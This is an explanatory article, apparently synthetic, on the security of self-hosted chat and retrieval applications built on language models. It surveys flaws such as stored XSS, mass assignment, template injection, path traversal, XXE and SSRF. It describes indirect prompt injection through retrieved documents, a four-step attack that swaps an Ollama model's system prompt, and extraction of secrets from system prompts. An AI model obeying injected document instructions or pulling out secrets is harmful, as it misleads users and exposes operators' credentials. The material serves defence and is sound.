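# Security of self-hosted chat and document-retrieval applications built on language models

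## What do these applications store, and who can reach it?

A language model takes in text and produces more text. Most people use one through a separate application that adds a web page, user accounts and saved conversations. OpenAI runs one such application, ChatGPT. Open-source projects publish others that a person, company or university can install on its own server. A self-hosted application stores the conversations, reusable prompts and document collections of all its users, which makes the server worth attacking even when the model is ordinary.

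Open WebUI, one of the best known, is a general chat page for individuals and teams. AnythingLLM, from Mintplex Labs, is mainly for asking questions about one's own documents, and LibreChat is for talking to models from many providers in one place. Dify, from LangGenius, is a visual builder in which a developer draws a workflow and publishes the result as an API (an interface for other programs) or as a chat box on another website. The people typing into it may therefore be strangers to the operator. These descriptions are based on Open WebUI's (2026) comparison of itself with its rivals.

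Most people who host one of these applications want to keep their data private. In *Exploring and Exploiting Security Vulnerabilities in Self-Hosted LLM Services*, Liu, Hu and colleagues (2026) attribute the trend to control over private data, independence from a provider and freedom to customise. Cost matters too, since Open WebUI's community edition is free for any number of users and the operator pays only for hardware or for a provider's metered service. A single page can also offer models from several makers, some running locally and some paid for by use.

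Privacy depends on where the model runs. The front end is the web application, which has its own server and database. A separate model backend, either a local program such as Ollama or a provider's API, runs the model and answers the front end's requests. An operator who connects Open WebUI to OpenAI still sends OpenAI every question and any accompanying document text.

### One question, from browser to answer

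Suppose a small engineering firm runs Open WebUI, and an employee wants to know how much she can claim for a hotel in Graz. The answer is in a travel policy that the office manager uploaded months ago.

When the PDF was uploaded, the front end ingested it by extracting the text, cutting it into chunks and indexing them. According to Open WebUI's *Retrieval Augmented Generation (RAG)*, the software measures chunks in characters by default, and neighbouring chunks can share some text so that a sentence on the boundary keeps its context. An embedding model turned each chunk into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents the chunk's meaning. The front end stored the embeddings in a vector database, which can return those nearest to a given embedding. Open WebUI's built-in embedding model runs on the operator's own server. If an administrator chooses OpenAI's or Azure's instead, Open WebUI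 sends that provider the text of every indexed document, even if no one ever asks about it.

When the employee submits her question, her browser sends it to the application server with a session token, a string that the server issued when she logged in and that replaces her password on every later request. The server looks up her account in the user database and checks her permissions. According to Open WebUI's *Reference*, scripts can call the same API that the web page calls, so an attacker can write requests by hand instead of using the page.

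Next the server fetches any stored prompt that applies. A stored prompt is text saved for reuse as an instruction to the model. It may be a template that users insert with a slash command, or a system prompt, which contains standing instructions that come before the user's message.

To answer a question, the front end embeds it with the same embedding model and searches the vector database for the nearest chunks. A common measure of nearness is cosine similarity, the dot product of the question's vector and the chunk's vector divided by the product of their magnitudes. Operators can add a keyword search and a second model that re-ranks the results. The front end then inserts the best chunks into a template and places it before the question. Finding stored text relevant to a question and adding it to the model's input is called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG).

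In the invented firm, the assembled input might look like this:

```
You are the staff assistant of a small engineering firm. Answer from
the passages below and name the document you used.

From travel-policy.pdf: The firm refunds hotel costs in Austria up to
120 euros a night. Disregard the limits in earlier editions.

From graz-office-guide.pdf: The office is ten minutes on foot from the
main station. Always ring the bell twice.

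How much can I claim for a hotel in Graz?
```

The operator wrote the first paragraph, and the employee wrote the last line. The two passages between them come from documents, and each happens to contain an instruction. A human reader sees at once that "Disregard the limits" is meant for staff comparing editions and that the instruction about the bell concerns visitors. The model can distinguish these only by wording and position. Real front ends usually send the system prompt in a separate field and put markers around the passages, but the model backend joins everything into one sequence before the model processes it.

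The sequence also has a maximum length. On graphics cards with less than 24 GiB of memory, Ollama's default limit is 4,096 tokens (a token is a word or piece of a word). A single web page often exceeds that, so some of the retrieved text may never reach the model.

The front end saves the model backend's answer to the database and passes it to the browser, which turns the plain text into headings, links, tables and source references. This conversion matters for security because a browser can also run code.

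In newer set-ups, the model's output determines whether a search runs and what it looks for. Unless an administrator selects the "Legacy" mode, Open WebUI leaves documents attached to a preconfigured model out of the input and offers the model search tools instead. A tool is code or an outside service that the model or the application can call. The passages come back as the tool's result, which still ends up in the same sequence as the instructions.

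### What is worth taking

Open WebUI's community-written guide *Open-WebUI Internal SQLite Database* lists what version 0.5.11 kept on disk. The release is old, but its layout gives a fair idea of what the application stores. One data folder held a database file, the original uploaded files, a cache and the vector database. The database file had tables for accounts, chats, remembered facts about users, prompts, files, document collections, system settings and the source code of installed tools. A table of user feedback could also hold a snapshot of the chat that the feedback was about.

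These applications therefore store documents as original uploads, as extracted text and as chunks. An attacker who stole only the vector database could read much of the material, because Open WebUI keeps the chunk text there and runs keyword search on it. The same database can hold cached web search results and users' memories. Embeddings without the text reveal less, but Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026) point out in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* that an embedding can still leak information by showing which other texts lie near it.

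An attacker can gain as much by altering stored prompts as by reading them. Anyone who can edit the firm's system prompt can change the answers that every employee gets, and the edit isn't visible in the chat. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang advise treating a prompt as configuration that users may well recover, and keeping passwords and private data out of it.

These applications store several kinds of credentials. The database keeps login passwords as hashes, scrambled forms that an attacker must crack to recover the passwords. A stolen session token can be used as it is until it expires or the server revokes it. API keys, which users create for their scripts, carry the permissions of the person who made them. Provider keys let the front end spend money at OpenAI or elsewhere, and some also grant broader access. Open WebUI's *Role-Based Access Control (RBAC)* warns operators against connecting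 a gateway's management or master key for ordinary traffic, because the provider does not enforce the front end's permissions.

Intruders can also use the application's computing power. *Unveiling the Landscape of LLM Deployment in the Wild* (Hou, Han and colleagues, 2025) lists the hijacking of graphics processors among the risks of an open Ollama server. If the application uses a model through a paid API, the operator pays for the intruder's usage.

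### Five attackers

An anonymous visitor knows the server's address and can read the application's code, which is open source. According to Open WebUI's *Security Policy*, the visitor can also, by design, reach the sign-in and registration functions and the public settings that the login screen needs. Registration is open by default, though new accounts normally remain "pending" until an administrator approves them. AnythingLLM's *Feature Overview* describes a single-user mode in which the password is optional, so a stranger who finds an unprotected copy can start using it. If the operator has also exposed a model backend such as Ollama, whose API requires no login by default, the visitor can bypass the front end.

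A new installation is vulnerable during first registration because the first person to register becomes its administrator. In Open WebUI before 0.9.0, several people registering at the same time could all become administrators. Since 0.9.0, none of them would, according to Open WebUI's *Known & Accepted Risks*.

A registered user with few rights has a valid session token, can talk to the model, and can often upload files. An attacker with such an account would try to reach other people's material. Some defaults are fairly tight. Open WebUI's *Workspace* states that ordinary users cannot open the tabs for shared models, document collections, prompts or tools until an administrator allows it. A workspace is generally a named area that groups documents, prompts, chats and settings, and that users may share, as in AnythingLLM. In Open WebUI, the word refers to a whole section of the site, and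 people share single items from it. Joining a group in Open WebUI can widen a user's rights but never narrow them.

Users can share material with more people than they expect. TU Wien Datalab tells users of the installation at TU Wien, a university in Vienna, that any logged-in user with the link to a shared chat can read it. LibreChat's *Access Control* stresses that the permission to share an agent (a model set up with its own instructions and tools) with chosen people is separate from the permission to show it to everyone on the server.

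The third attacker never contacts the server. This outsider writes something that an insider will bring in, such as a supplier's letter, a job application or a web page. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang call this attacker an external-content adversary. The attacker can use the document to target the software that extracts its text or the model that later receives a chunk of it. According to Open WebUI's *LLM Output Unpredictability*, the second attack is limited because a model acting for a user cannot do anything that the user could not. This is a real limit, but the user is the victim, so if an administrator asks about the letter, its author can exploit an administrator's permissions.

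Attacks can come from a shared plugin or from an upstream service that the front end trusts, such as a model server, an embedding service or a tool server. GCVE's *GHSA-CM35-V4VP-5XVX* (2025) describes a case in Open WebUI 0.6.33 and earlier. Users could connect their own choice of model server, and a hostile server could reply with an event that ran a script in the user's browser and stole the session token. The attacker had to persuade the victim to add the server, and the feature was off by default. Once someone has installed a malicious plugin, the attacker has less persuading to do, because the plugin runs as code on the application's server.

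Administrators have access to nearly everything by default. Open WebUI treats them all as trusted, within a single trust boundary, and generally declines vulnerability reports that depend on an administrator doing something unsafe. That is a reasonable way to decide which bugs to fix, but it is less reassuring to employees whose chats are on the machine. Anyone who controls the host can copy the entire database file with one command, whatever the front end's permission settings. An intruder who steals an administrator's session gains that administrator's access.

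### The basic kinds of flaw

Broken access control is a missing or wrong check on whether a user may perform an action or see a record. Early versions of Open WebUI had this flaw. *GHSA-4vg5-rp28-gvjf*, an entry in OSV, a public database of flaws in open-source software, explains that the page kept pending users out until an administrator approved them, but the API behind it did not check their status. Anyone could register and call the API directly as a normal user.

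Path traversal is the use of a crafted file name to read or write outside the intended folder. A front end might save each upload under the name the sender gave it. If that name contains steps meaning "go up one folder" and the software follows them, the upload can overwrite a settings file.

In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker makes a server fetch an address that the attacker can't reach directly. These applications normally fetch web pages at a user's request. In Open WebUI, for example, a user types a hash sign and a web address, and the server reads the page into the chat. If the server also accepts the address of an internal machine, such as the firm's payroll system, the user can read a page that the firewall is meant to block.

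In cross-site scripting (XSS), an attacker's script runs in someone else's browser as part of a page the browser trusts. In stored XSS, the script is in saved content and runs for anyone who views it later. A user could hide a script in a chat and share the link. When a colleague opens the chat, the script can act with the colleague's rights and perhaps copy the session token.

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is indirect when the text arrives in a document or web page instead of the attacker's own message. In the Graz example, a hotel's brochure might include a sentence telling the assistant to recommend that hotel regardless of what the policy allows. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang use the narrower term "jailbreaking" for getting a model to break its safety rules, while prompt injection also covers stealing data and misusing tools.

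A CVE number identifies one publicly recorded flaw, CWE is a catalogue of weakness types, and CVSS is a severity score from 0 to 10. The pending-user flaw is CVE-2026-44567, and its weakness types include CWE-602, which means enforcing a rule in the browser when the server should enforce it. Open WebUI 0.1.124 fixed the flaw. The fix is older than the CVE number suggests, because the record dates from May 2026, when the project was already far past version 0.6.33.

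OSV's *CVE-2026-44567* lists the flaw's score as 7.3, or "high". An attacker can exploit it over the network with little difficulty, no prior privileges and no help from a victim. The harm to confidentiality, integrity and availability is rated low in each case. Under the CVSS version 3.1 formula, ease of attack contributes about 3.89 points and harm about 3.37, and the total rounds up to 7.3. Because a flaw can score high mostly by being easy to exploit, operators need the individual ratings as well as the score to know what an intruder would gain.

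The public records of these vulnerabilities have gaps. By Open WebUI's account, it published 19 advisories in late September 2026, before GitHub had assigned the CVE numbers it had requested. On October 12, VulnCheck, which can also issue CVE numbers, published its own records for all 19. The copies in GitHub's advisory database didn't list the affected package or versions, so GitHub's automatic alerts didn't reach anyone running the vulnerable software. Open WebUI now waits for GitHub to assign a number before publishing each advisory, which takes about four weeks or longer after the corrected release. Operators who wait for an advisory before updating keep running the vulnerable version during that time, even though a fix is available.

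## What can go wrong with a stored prompt?

The damage a stored prompt can do depends on which program handles it. The browser displays it as page content, the database stores it as a record with an owner, some template engines run it as code, and the model follows it as an instruction. If an administrator has written a password into the prompt, the prompt is also a secret, and it is usually poorly protected.

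### Prompts that run scripts in the browser

A publicly shared prompt appears in every Open WebUI user's list of slash commands, according to Open WebUI's *Prompts*. Before version 0.6.35, a prompt could run a script in the browser of the user who inserted it.

The flaw, CVE-2025-64495, was in an option named "Insert Prompt as Rich Text". With the option on, the page passed the saved prompt through marked, a library that converts lightly formatted text into HTML, the language of web pages. HTML can contain scripts, and marked does not remove them. The page then put the HTML directly into one of its elements, and the browser ran any script in it. This happened when the user inserted the prompt, before they had sent anything to the model.

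GitHub's *GHSA-W7XJ-8FX7-WFCH* (2025) lists two preconditions for the attack. The attacker needs permission to create prompts, which ordinary users lack by default but may receive through a group. The victim must have turned on the rich-text option, which is off by default in their preferences. If the victim then inserts the attacker's prompt, a script in it can read the victim's session token from the browser's storage and send it to the attacker. If the victim is an administrator, the attacker can then run commands on the server, because administrators are allowed to install Python code there.

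OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1741* (2026) lists the CVSS base score as 8.7, or "high". A base score assumes that the vulnerable setting is in use, so it isn't lowered because this flaw depends on an unusual one. The score is also raised for "changed scope", meaning that the harm reaches beyond the component with the flaw. If the scope were unchanged and the other ratings stayed the same, the score would be 7.3. Both scores greatly overstate the danger to an installation where only administrators could write prompts.

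All versions up to 0.6.34 have the flaw. The advisory recommends passing the converted prompt through DOMPurify, a library that strips scripts out of HTML, before the page uses it. An operator who can't update immediately can remove the prompt permission from groups that don't need it and ask users to turn the option off, starting with administrators.

### Prompts as database records

A front end stores a prompt's text in a record with a name, an author and other fields, and the editing form shows only some of them. In LibreChat 0.8.0 and earlier, the server did not enforce the form's limits, a vulnerability recorded as CVE-2025-66451.

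LibreChat files saved prompts in "prompt groups". When a user edits a group, the browser sends the server a list of fields with their new values. According to *CVE-2025-66451 Detail* (2025), an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database, LibreChat passed this list to the function that updates the database without filtering out sensitive fields. A user who wrote the request by hand could therefore add fields that the form did not include. Programmers call this weakness mass assignment, catalogued as CWE-915.

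The most obvious field for an attacker to add to a request is the author field. Cybersecurity Help's *Improper access control in LibreChat* (2026) describes how an attacker can gain access to a prompt by changing its recorded author. Ownership determines who may manage a prompt, so the attacker in effect changes its permissions without opening the sharing settings. The rightful owner can then no longer edit the prompt, according to *CVE-2025-66451*, an AI-generated summary by the security company Wiz. LibreChat 0.8.1 fixes the flaw. Wiz says it rejects any request that contains a protected field.

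The public ratings differ on who can carry out the attack. The score listed in NVD, 5.3 (medium), is for an attacker without an account. Cybersecurity Help assumes a logged-in user with few rights and rates the severity low. The second assumption fits better because the function is for editing prompts and Wiz also describes a logged-in attacker.

The same mistake had already appeared elsewhere in LibreChat. In CVE-2025-7104, published in September 2025, extra fields in a request could overwrite the author and access level of an agent, which stores instructions much as a prompt does. CVELogic, which collects vulnerability records, lists the flaw with a score of 7.5. The prompt-group flaw became public less than three months later. A filter in one update function doesn't protect the others, so developers have to define the permitted fields for each.

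Other flaws occur when the server checks the wrong record or none at all. OSV's *CVE-2024-11167* (2025) reports that before LibreChat 0.7.6, a logged-in user could delete another person's prompt by supplying its identifier, because the server did not check who owned it. In version 0.7.5, users could also create, use and share prompts without the administrator's permission, according to OSV's *CVE-2024-10363* (2025).

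Open WebUI had a less obvious flaw in its version history, which keeps the old versions of a prompt whenever someone saves a change. A request to compare two versions contains the identifiers of the prompt and of both versions. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2701* (2026) explains that the server checked whether the user could read the prompt but not whether the versions belonged to it. An attacker could send the identifier of their own prompt with the identifiers of versions of someone else's, and the server would return the other person's text.

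The function for restoring an old version lacked the same check, so an attacker could copy a stranger's text into their own prompt and read it there. The function for deleting a version lacked it too. The function for reading a single version did include the check, which suggests an oversight more than a misunderstanding. The attacker needed the identifiers of the victim's versions, which are long and hard to guess, and could delete a prompt's history but not the current prompt. OSV's *CVE-2026-54015* (2026) gives the flaw a score of 6.4 and lists versions before 0.9.6 as affected.

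### Prompts as template code

Many stored prompts contain blanks. The office manager in the invented engineering firm might save this one:

```
Write a hotel claim for {{name}}, who spent {{nights}} nights in Graz.
```

A front end can treat the double braces in two ways. The simpler is to treat them as placeholders and replace each name the software knows with its value. If the manager writes `{{nights * 120}}` to get the maximum refund, the software calculates nothing, because it has no value under that name.

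The other way is to evaluate an expression. Jinja2, a template language for Python programs, would calculate the contents of the same braces and insert 360 for a stay of three nights. It also has loops and conditions, so a template can list every document in a collection or add a paragraph only for new employees.

If the server evaluates a stored prompt as a template, anyone who can edit the template can write a program that the server runs. In Python, even a piece of text is an object with links to its type, and from there to other parts of the running software. In an attack called server-side template injection, an attacker can follow these links to a function that executes operating-system commands. The usual protection is a sandbox, a restricted mode that prevents the template engine from following the dangerous links.

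GitHub's *GHSA-793V-GXFP-9Q9H* (2025) documents a flaw in spacy-llm, a Python library that connects language models to the text-analysis toolkit spaCy. In version 0.7.2 and earlier, an attacker could run arbitrary code by putting a crafted expression in the template field. Version 0.7.3 fixes the flaw. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-25362* (2025), the entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists a score of 9.8, or "critical". That score is fair for applications that let strangers supply templates, but when developers write all the templates, an outsider must first gain access some other way.

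Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild*, use this advisory to argue that ordinary weakness labels are incomplete. Its label, CWE-94, means code injection. They write that the attack works through template-based prompts and model-generated content, neither of which the label conveys. They are right about prompts, but the advisory's description mentions only the template field. An attacker who controls the template does not need the model to produce anything, because the code runs while the server is still assembling the prompt.

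Other software for building prompts has had similar problems. GitHub's *GHSA-6QV9-48XG-FC7F* (2025) describes how prompt templates in LangChain, a widely used framework for applications based on language models, gave attackers access to the internals of Python objects. Model files can also include a chat template, which arranges the system prompt and the messages in the format that the model expects. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-392* (severity score 9.6), llama-cpp-python, a package for running models locally, rendered this template in Jinja2 without a sandbox, so loading a stranger's model file could also run the stranger's code.

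The documentation for the Open WebUI front end describes prompt variables as placeholders. Open WebUI fills some with values such as the date or the user's name, and opens a form with text fields, menus and date pickers for others. The syntax also supports features such as default values and shortening long text to a set number of characters, but the documentation describes no general expressions.

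Dify does evaluate templates. Its "Template node" is a workflow step that formats text with Jinja2, including its loops, conditionals and filters. In August 2026 a flaw in the code that handles these templates became public as CVE-2026-18632. It affects versions up to 1.14.2. Exploiting it requires a login, and an exploit is in circulation. According to OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-18632* (2026), the company did not respond when told of the problem. The CVE record lists no fixed version. An AI-generated note on the same page recommends version 1.15, but nothing in the record supports that, so operators should confirm it with Dify before relying on it.

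The AI-generated note also lists arbitrary code execution as a possibility, but the record itself gives the flaw a score of 5.3, with low ratings for harm to confidentiality, integrity and availability. Dify already lets developers write templates, so the flaw matters most to operators who let people build workflows but don't trust them with the server.

Software that fills placeholders without evaluating expressions can still leak secrets if users can write placeholders for them. LibreChat up to version 0.8.3 had this flaw in its handling of tool server addresses, rather than stored prompts. It let users connect their own tool servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for linking models to tools. Debian's *CVE-2026-32625* describes how LibreChat filled placeholders in the server's address from its own environment variables, where operators commonly keep secrets. A user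 could enter the address of a machine they controlled, with placeholders for LibreChat's encryption keys and database address, and LibreChat would send those values to that machine.

Open WebUI fills the placeholders in a prompt with data from the person using it. This data can include the user's email address, location and clipboard contents, though the last two need permission from the user or the browser. If a colleague used a shared prompt containing the clipboard placeholder, whatever they had last copied could be inserted into their message, sent to the model backend and saved in their chat history. The prompt's author would still need a way to retrieve the text.

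### Prompts that mislead the model

A malicious prompt can work without a software flaw. Suppose someone at the engineering firm shares a forty-line template for summarising contracts, and one line tells the model to leave out penalty clauses. The front end stores the template correctly, the browser displays it safely, and the model follows the instructions. Every colleague who uses the command gets a fluent summary that omits the penalty clauses.

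Users have a chance to read a template when they use it, and it is worth reading an imported template before sharing it further. A malicious system prompt is harder to catch because it applies to every chat without appearing in any of them. An attacker can also use the database flaws to take over a trusted prompt's record and rewrite the instruction under a name that people already use.

Open WebUI's version history for saved prompts shows who made each change and when, and an editor can restore an earlier version. The history is weaker as evidence after an attack, because users can delete any entry except the version in current use.

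An attacker can also change the instructions outside the front end. Liu and colleagues tested this on Ollama as part of LENS, their framework for probing self-hosted services. A model in Ollama can carry a system prompt of its own, and an Ollama server that is open to the internet lets any visitor manage its models. The attack has four steps:

1. The attacker asks the server which models it has.
2. The attacker copies one of them under a different name.
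3. The attacker deletes the original.
4. From the copy, the attacker creates a model with the original's name and a new system prompt.

A front end that requests the model by name now gets the altered one. The front end's model list looks the same, and its prompt history doesn't record the change because nobody edited a prompt there.

In August 2025 the researchers sampled 9,999 of the 384,588 Ollama records in FOFA, a search engine for internet-connected machines. After removing duplicates, they found 1,811 live servers, of which only 430 gave a usable response to their probes. They judged the complete attack achievable on 417 servers, which is 97% of those that gave a usable response and 23% of all the live ones. The higher figure means that almost nothing prevents the attack once an Ollama server answers requests from strangers.

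An attack described as "achievable" was not necessarily carried out. On third-party servers, the researchers kept their requests to the minimum needed to judge the response. They counted a blank reply to a copy or delete request as a success if the server reported no error. The test therefore measured whether the functions needed for an attack were open, not how many people an attacker could mislead or for how long.

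To show what a replaced prompt can do, the researchers gave a copy of Llama 3 a misleading system prompt and asked it how to secure a home wireless network. It recommended WEP, an encryption method that has been obsolete for years, sensibly suggested a separate network for guests, and advised turning off the router's firewall. Mixing good advice with bad makes the attack hard to notice, because a user who checks one piece of advice and finds it sound has a reason to trust the rest.

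To prevent this, the operator has to keep strangers away from the model backend, either by placing it on a private network or by requiring a login. Tighter permissions in the front end would not have stopped it. An operator who suspects tampering should check the system prompt stored with the model in Ollama as well as the one in the front end.

### Why a system prompt cannot keep a secret

OWASP, a non-profit organisation for software security, lists "system prompt leakage" as one of ten risks for applications built on language models. Shifat and colleagues summarise the category as the exposure of system prompts that contain sensitive instructions or data. A prompt can leak through the front end or through the model, and a patch exists only for front-end leaks.

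Administrators of Open WebUI let colleagues use a preconfigured model by granting them read access to it. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-45387* (2026), in versions before 0.9.5 that access also let them read the model's system prompt, without having to trick the model into revealing it. Corgea, a security company, documents what looks like the same exposure in version 0.6.40. After an ordinary user logged in, the web page routinely requested the list of available models, and the server's reply included the system prompts that the administrator had set. The user could have read them in the browser's developer tools.

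The flaw scores 4.3, or "medium", and Open WebUI treated it as a security issue because people may consider their system prompts confidential. The organisation that issued CVE-2024-7045, an older report with the same ratings, withdrew it in August 2026. That report concerned version 0.3.8, in which any approved user could read every saved prompt. Open WebUI's *CVE-2024-7045* (2026) argues persuasively that this was the purpose of the feature, because prompts in that version were slash commands for everyone and the software had no private ones. A field labelled "prompt" may be private in one version and public in another, so operators have reason to check whether the installed version keeps it private before writing anything sensitive there.

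The update to 0.9.5 closes the leak in the front end, but the model still receives the system prompt with every chat and can repeat it. An instruction to keep the prompt confidential doesn't reliably prevent this, because the model processes it as text along with the user's request. Liu and colleagues showed that documents can leak in the same way. On a volunteer's AnythingLLM server, a visitor could not open the stored files but could get the model to reveal their contents with a carefully worded question.

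Anyone who can talk to the model and is patient enough to try different questions can get a password or provider key out of its system prompt. If an outside company hosts the model, that company also receives the key with each message. A key belongs in the server-side settings of the tool that needs it. The tool can then call the service the key is for and give the model only the result.

Access rules fail for a related reason. Suppose the firm's system prompt includes an instruction to discuss salaries only with managers. The model cannot reliably identify managers, and an employee can claim to be one. The prompt could include details from the user's account, but some of these are also unreliable. For example, Open WebUI has a placeholder for the user's bio, which users write themselves. Even with a trustworthy job title in the input, enforcing the rule would depend on the model following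 the instruction correctly every time, and some users have a motive to manipulate it.

The front end can check the account's permissions before it searches the documents. If an employee isn't allowed to see the salary file, the front end leaves it out of the model's input, so the model can't disclose it however the question is worded.

A secret can still leak after it is deleted from a prompt. Open WebUI keeps the earlier version in the prompt's history, and database backups may hold further copies. The flaw fixed in version 0.9.6 exposed this history to other users. An administrator who finds a key in a stored prompt should revoke it with the provider and issue a new one.

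## How can an uploaded or fetched document attack the server?

Before a model reads a document, the front end has to receive the file, choose where to store it, unpack it if it is an archive, and extract its text. If the document is a web page or belongs to a connected wiki, the server also has to fetch it. These steps run ordinary code on material that an outsider may have written. Hidden instructions can affect the model only after these steps, so the choice of model makes no difference to the attacks described here.

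### File names that lead out of the folder

A browser sends a file's name along with its contents, and an attacker who writes the request by hand can choose any name. Early versions of Open WebUI did not clean this name before using it to store the file, so users could write files anywhere the web server's account could, according to *CVE-2026-44566*, an entry from Croatia's national computer emergency team, CERT.hr. Version 0.1.124 fixed this for files attached to a prompt. Audio uploads had the same flaw until version 0.6.10, according to CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-44565*.

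Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-59379* describes a similar flaw in Open WebUI's upload of model files and recommends keeping only the base name, the part of the path after the last slash. A program can also store each file under a random name and keep the original filename as a label in the database.

Neither method is enough when users can choose folders, because the server must then accept a path and check whether it is allowed. AnythingLLM has handled this check incorrectly in several ways.

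Suppose an application keeps its documents in `/srv/app/documents`, and a user requests `graz/../../notes.txt`. Two dots mean "go up one folder". The program joins the two paths and normalises the result, which means working through the dots until none are left:

```
Joined:       /srv/app/documents/graz/../../notes.txt
Normalised:   /srv/app/notes.txt
```

The normalised path is outside the documents folder, but it no longer contains "../", so a search for those characters finds nothing. Searching before normalisation would catch this request but miss one for the full path `/srv/app/notes.txt`, and it could miss a Windows path, which uses backslashes. Checking that the normalised path begins with `/srv/app/documents` doesn't work either, because `/srv/app/documents-old/notes.txt` passes this check but is in a different folder.

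A sound check works out the route from the permitted folder to the final path and rejects any route that leads upwards. In JavaScript, the language of AnythingLLM's server, it could look like this:

```
const root = fs.realpathSync("/srv/app/documents");
const target = fs.realpathSync(path.resolve(root, requested));
const route = path.relative(root, target);

const outside =
  route === ".." ||
  route.startsWith(".." + path.sep) ||
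  path.isAbsolute(route);

if (outside) throw new Error("Outside the documents folder");
```

In the example the route is `../notes.txt`, so the program stops. `path.sep` is a slash on Linux and a backslash on Windows. If a request names another Windows drive, no relative route exists and `path.relative` returns a full path, which the `isAbsolute` condition catches. `realpathSync` follows symbolic links, which are folder entries that point to files elsewhere. It works only on files that exist, so for a new file the program has to check the destination folder and then add a plain file name.

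AnythingLLM's shared check also used `path.relative`, but it rejected only the Linux-style "../". OSV's *CVE-2026-48789* (2026) explains that the check let through other results that the function returns on Windows, such as ".." alone. A user with few rights could send an encoded full path and list the contents of a folder outside the documents directory. The flaw affected only folder listing.

CVE-2024-10513 allowed a manager, an AnythingLLM role with rights between those of an ordinary user and an administrator, to do much more damage. The function for moving documents between folders also accepted the path of `anythingllm.db`, the application's database. According to Tenable's *CVE-2024-10513* (2025), a manager could move that file to a publicly accessible folder, download it and then delete it. The same release, 1.2.2, repaired `normalizePath`, which was supposed to clean paths. Exploit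 Intel's *CVE-2024-8248* (2025) describes how a manager could use the faulty function to read and write files in the storage directory and become an administrator.

The function also contributed to a vulnerability in agent flows, which are saved sequences of steps for an agent to carry out. AnythingLLM used it with `path.join` when loading or deleting a flow, which let requests reach files outside the flows folder. OSV's *CVE-2026-5627* (2026) reports that an attacker could read or delete any file ending in `.json` on the server. Some of these files hold API keys, and the application can't run without others.

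Some file paths become dangerous only after the application has checked them. According to AVID, a database of flaws in AI systems, AnythingLLM before 1.3.1 converted file names containing non-English characters in a way that could introduce "../", which the upload library did not remove. A manager or administrator could use this to write files elsewhere on the server. OSV's *CVE-2026-45403* (2026) describes a later flaw in a tool that lets AnythingLLM's agents copy files. The tool checked the folder being copied but not the symbolic links inside it, so a copy could include files from outside the permitted area. Version 1.13.0 fixes this flaw.

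File names can also come from a connected source. AnythingLLM can import pages from DrupalWiki, a commercial wiki system, and before version 1.10.0 a hostile wiki could make it write files anywhere on the server. Intruder, a security company, notes that an attacker could use this to run code, for example by overwriting a configuration file. The attacker had to be an administrator or persuade one to enter the hostile wiki's address.

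### Archives and parsers

Each file in a ZIP archive has a name that can include folders. If a program unpacks the archive without checking these names, an attacker can use a crafted name to place a file outside the intended folder. Programmers call this attack "zip slip".

RAGFlow, another open-source application for questioning documents, had this flaw in version 0.23.1 and possibly earlier. It can send documents to a MinerU server, which converts them and returns the result as a ZIP archive. According to CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-24770*, a malicious archive could overwrite any file and so lead to code execution. The record rates the attack as needing no login, but the archive comes from a server the operator chose, so the attacker would first have to take over or impersonate that server.

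AnythingLLM 1.11.1 and earlier had a zip slip flaw when importing plugins from its community hub, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-32719* (2026). Plugins are code, so installing a stranger's plugin already carries most of that risk.

Unstructured is a widely used Python library for extracting text from documents. Corgea's *Unstructured has Path Traversal via Malicious MSG Attachment* explains that an attacker could name an attachment in an Outlook message so that the library would write it anywhere on the disk, but only if the calling program had turned on attachment processing. OSV's *CVE-2025-64712* lists a severity score of 9.8, and version 0.18.18 fixes the flaw. An operator therefore needs to know which version of Unstructured the front end includes and whether the front end processes attachments.

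The parser flaw with the highest severity score is CVE-2025-66516 in Apache Tika, a toolkit that extracts text from many file formats. Open WebUI can use a separate Tika server instead of its own extraction code. The flaw allows an XML external entity (XXE) attack. XML is a text format in which a document can define an "external entity", a short name that stands for the contents of a file or web address. A vulnerable parser replaces the name with those contents, so if a document names a private file on the server, the file's contents can end up in the extracted text.

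A PDF can contain a form written in an XML format called XFA, and Apache Tika processed external entities in such forms. *CVE-2025-66516* (Allison, 2025) lists Tika's core package as affected from version 1.13 to 3.2.1. The notice extended an earlier one, CVE-2025-54988, to more Tika packages, so operators who had already updated had reason to check again. ThaiCERT's *Critical XML External Entity (XXE) Vulnerability Found in Apache Tika* (2025) gives the severity score as 10.0, the maximum.

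For a front end, the harm depends on where Tika runs. If Tika has its own container, it can read only that container's files, which normally don't include the front end's database, but it may be able to contact other internal machines. An attacker with an account could upload the PDF and look for the stolen text in the result. A supplier without an account could email the PDF to the office manager and wait for her to upload it. The supplier would then need another way to get the text back, such as an entity that makes Tika contact the supplier's server.

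Docling, another extraction program that Open WebUI supports, had a similar flaw in how it handled a format for scanned books. The June 2026 advisory, which CIRCL's *Common Weakness Enumeration* reproduces, also covers "zip bombs", small archives that expand until they fill the server's memory or disk. The usual ZIP compression can shrink very repetitive data about a thousandfold, so a 10 MB upload could expand to 10 GB. Limiting the size of uploads doesn't prevent this. The program has to count the bytes as it unpacks them and stop at a maximum.

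Word files are ZIP archives as well. GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration* includes an August 2026 flaw in Carbone, a document generator, where a crafted .docx file could exhaust the server's memory and crash it. Any front end that opens Word files needs protection against the same attack.

A front end can include a vulnerable library without being vulnerable itself. Snyk's *Improper Handling of Highly Compressed Data (Data Amplification) Affecting open-webui package* (2026) flags one company's packaged edition of Open WebUI because the package included a version of aiohttp, a Python networking library, with a zip bomb flaw. The flaw affects programs that use aiohttp to receive requests, but Open WebUI uses it to send them. An upload therefore probably can't trigger the flaw, though updating is easier than proving that it can't.

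### Making the server fetch a private page

Before version 0.6.37, Open WebUI's server did not check the address of a web page that a user asked it to import. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1726* (2026), any logged-in user could exploit this server-side request forgery (SSRF) flaw, CVE-2025-65958, to fetch a page from an internal machine such as a payroll system. The server returned the page's text as it would for any imported document.

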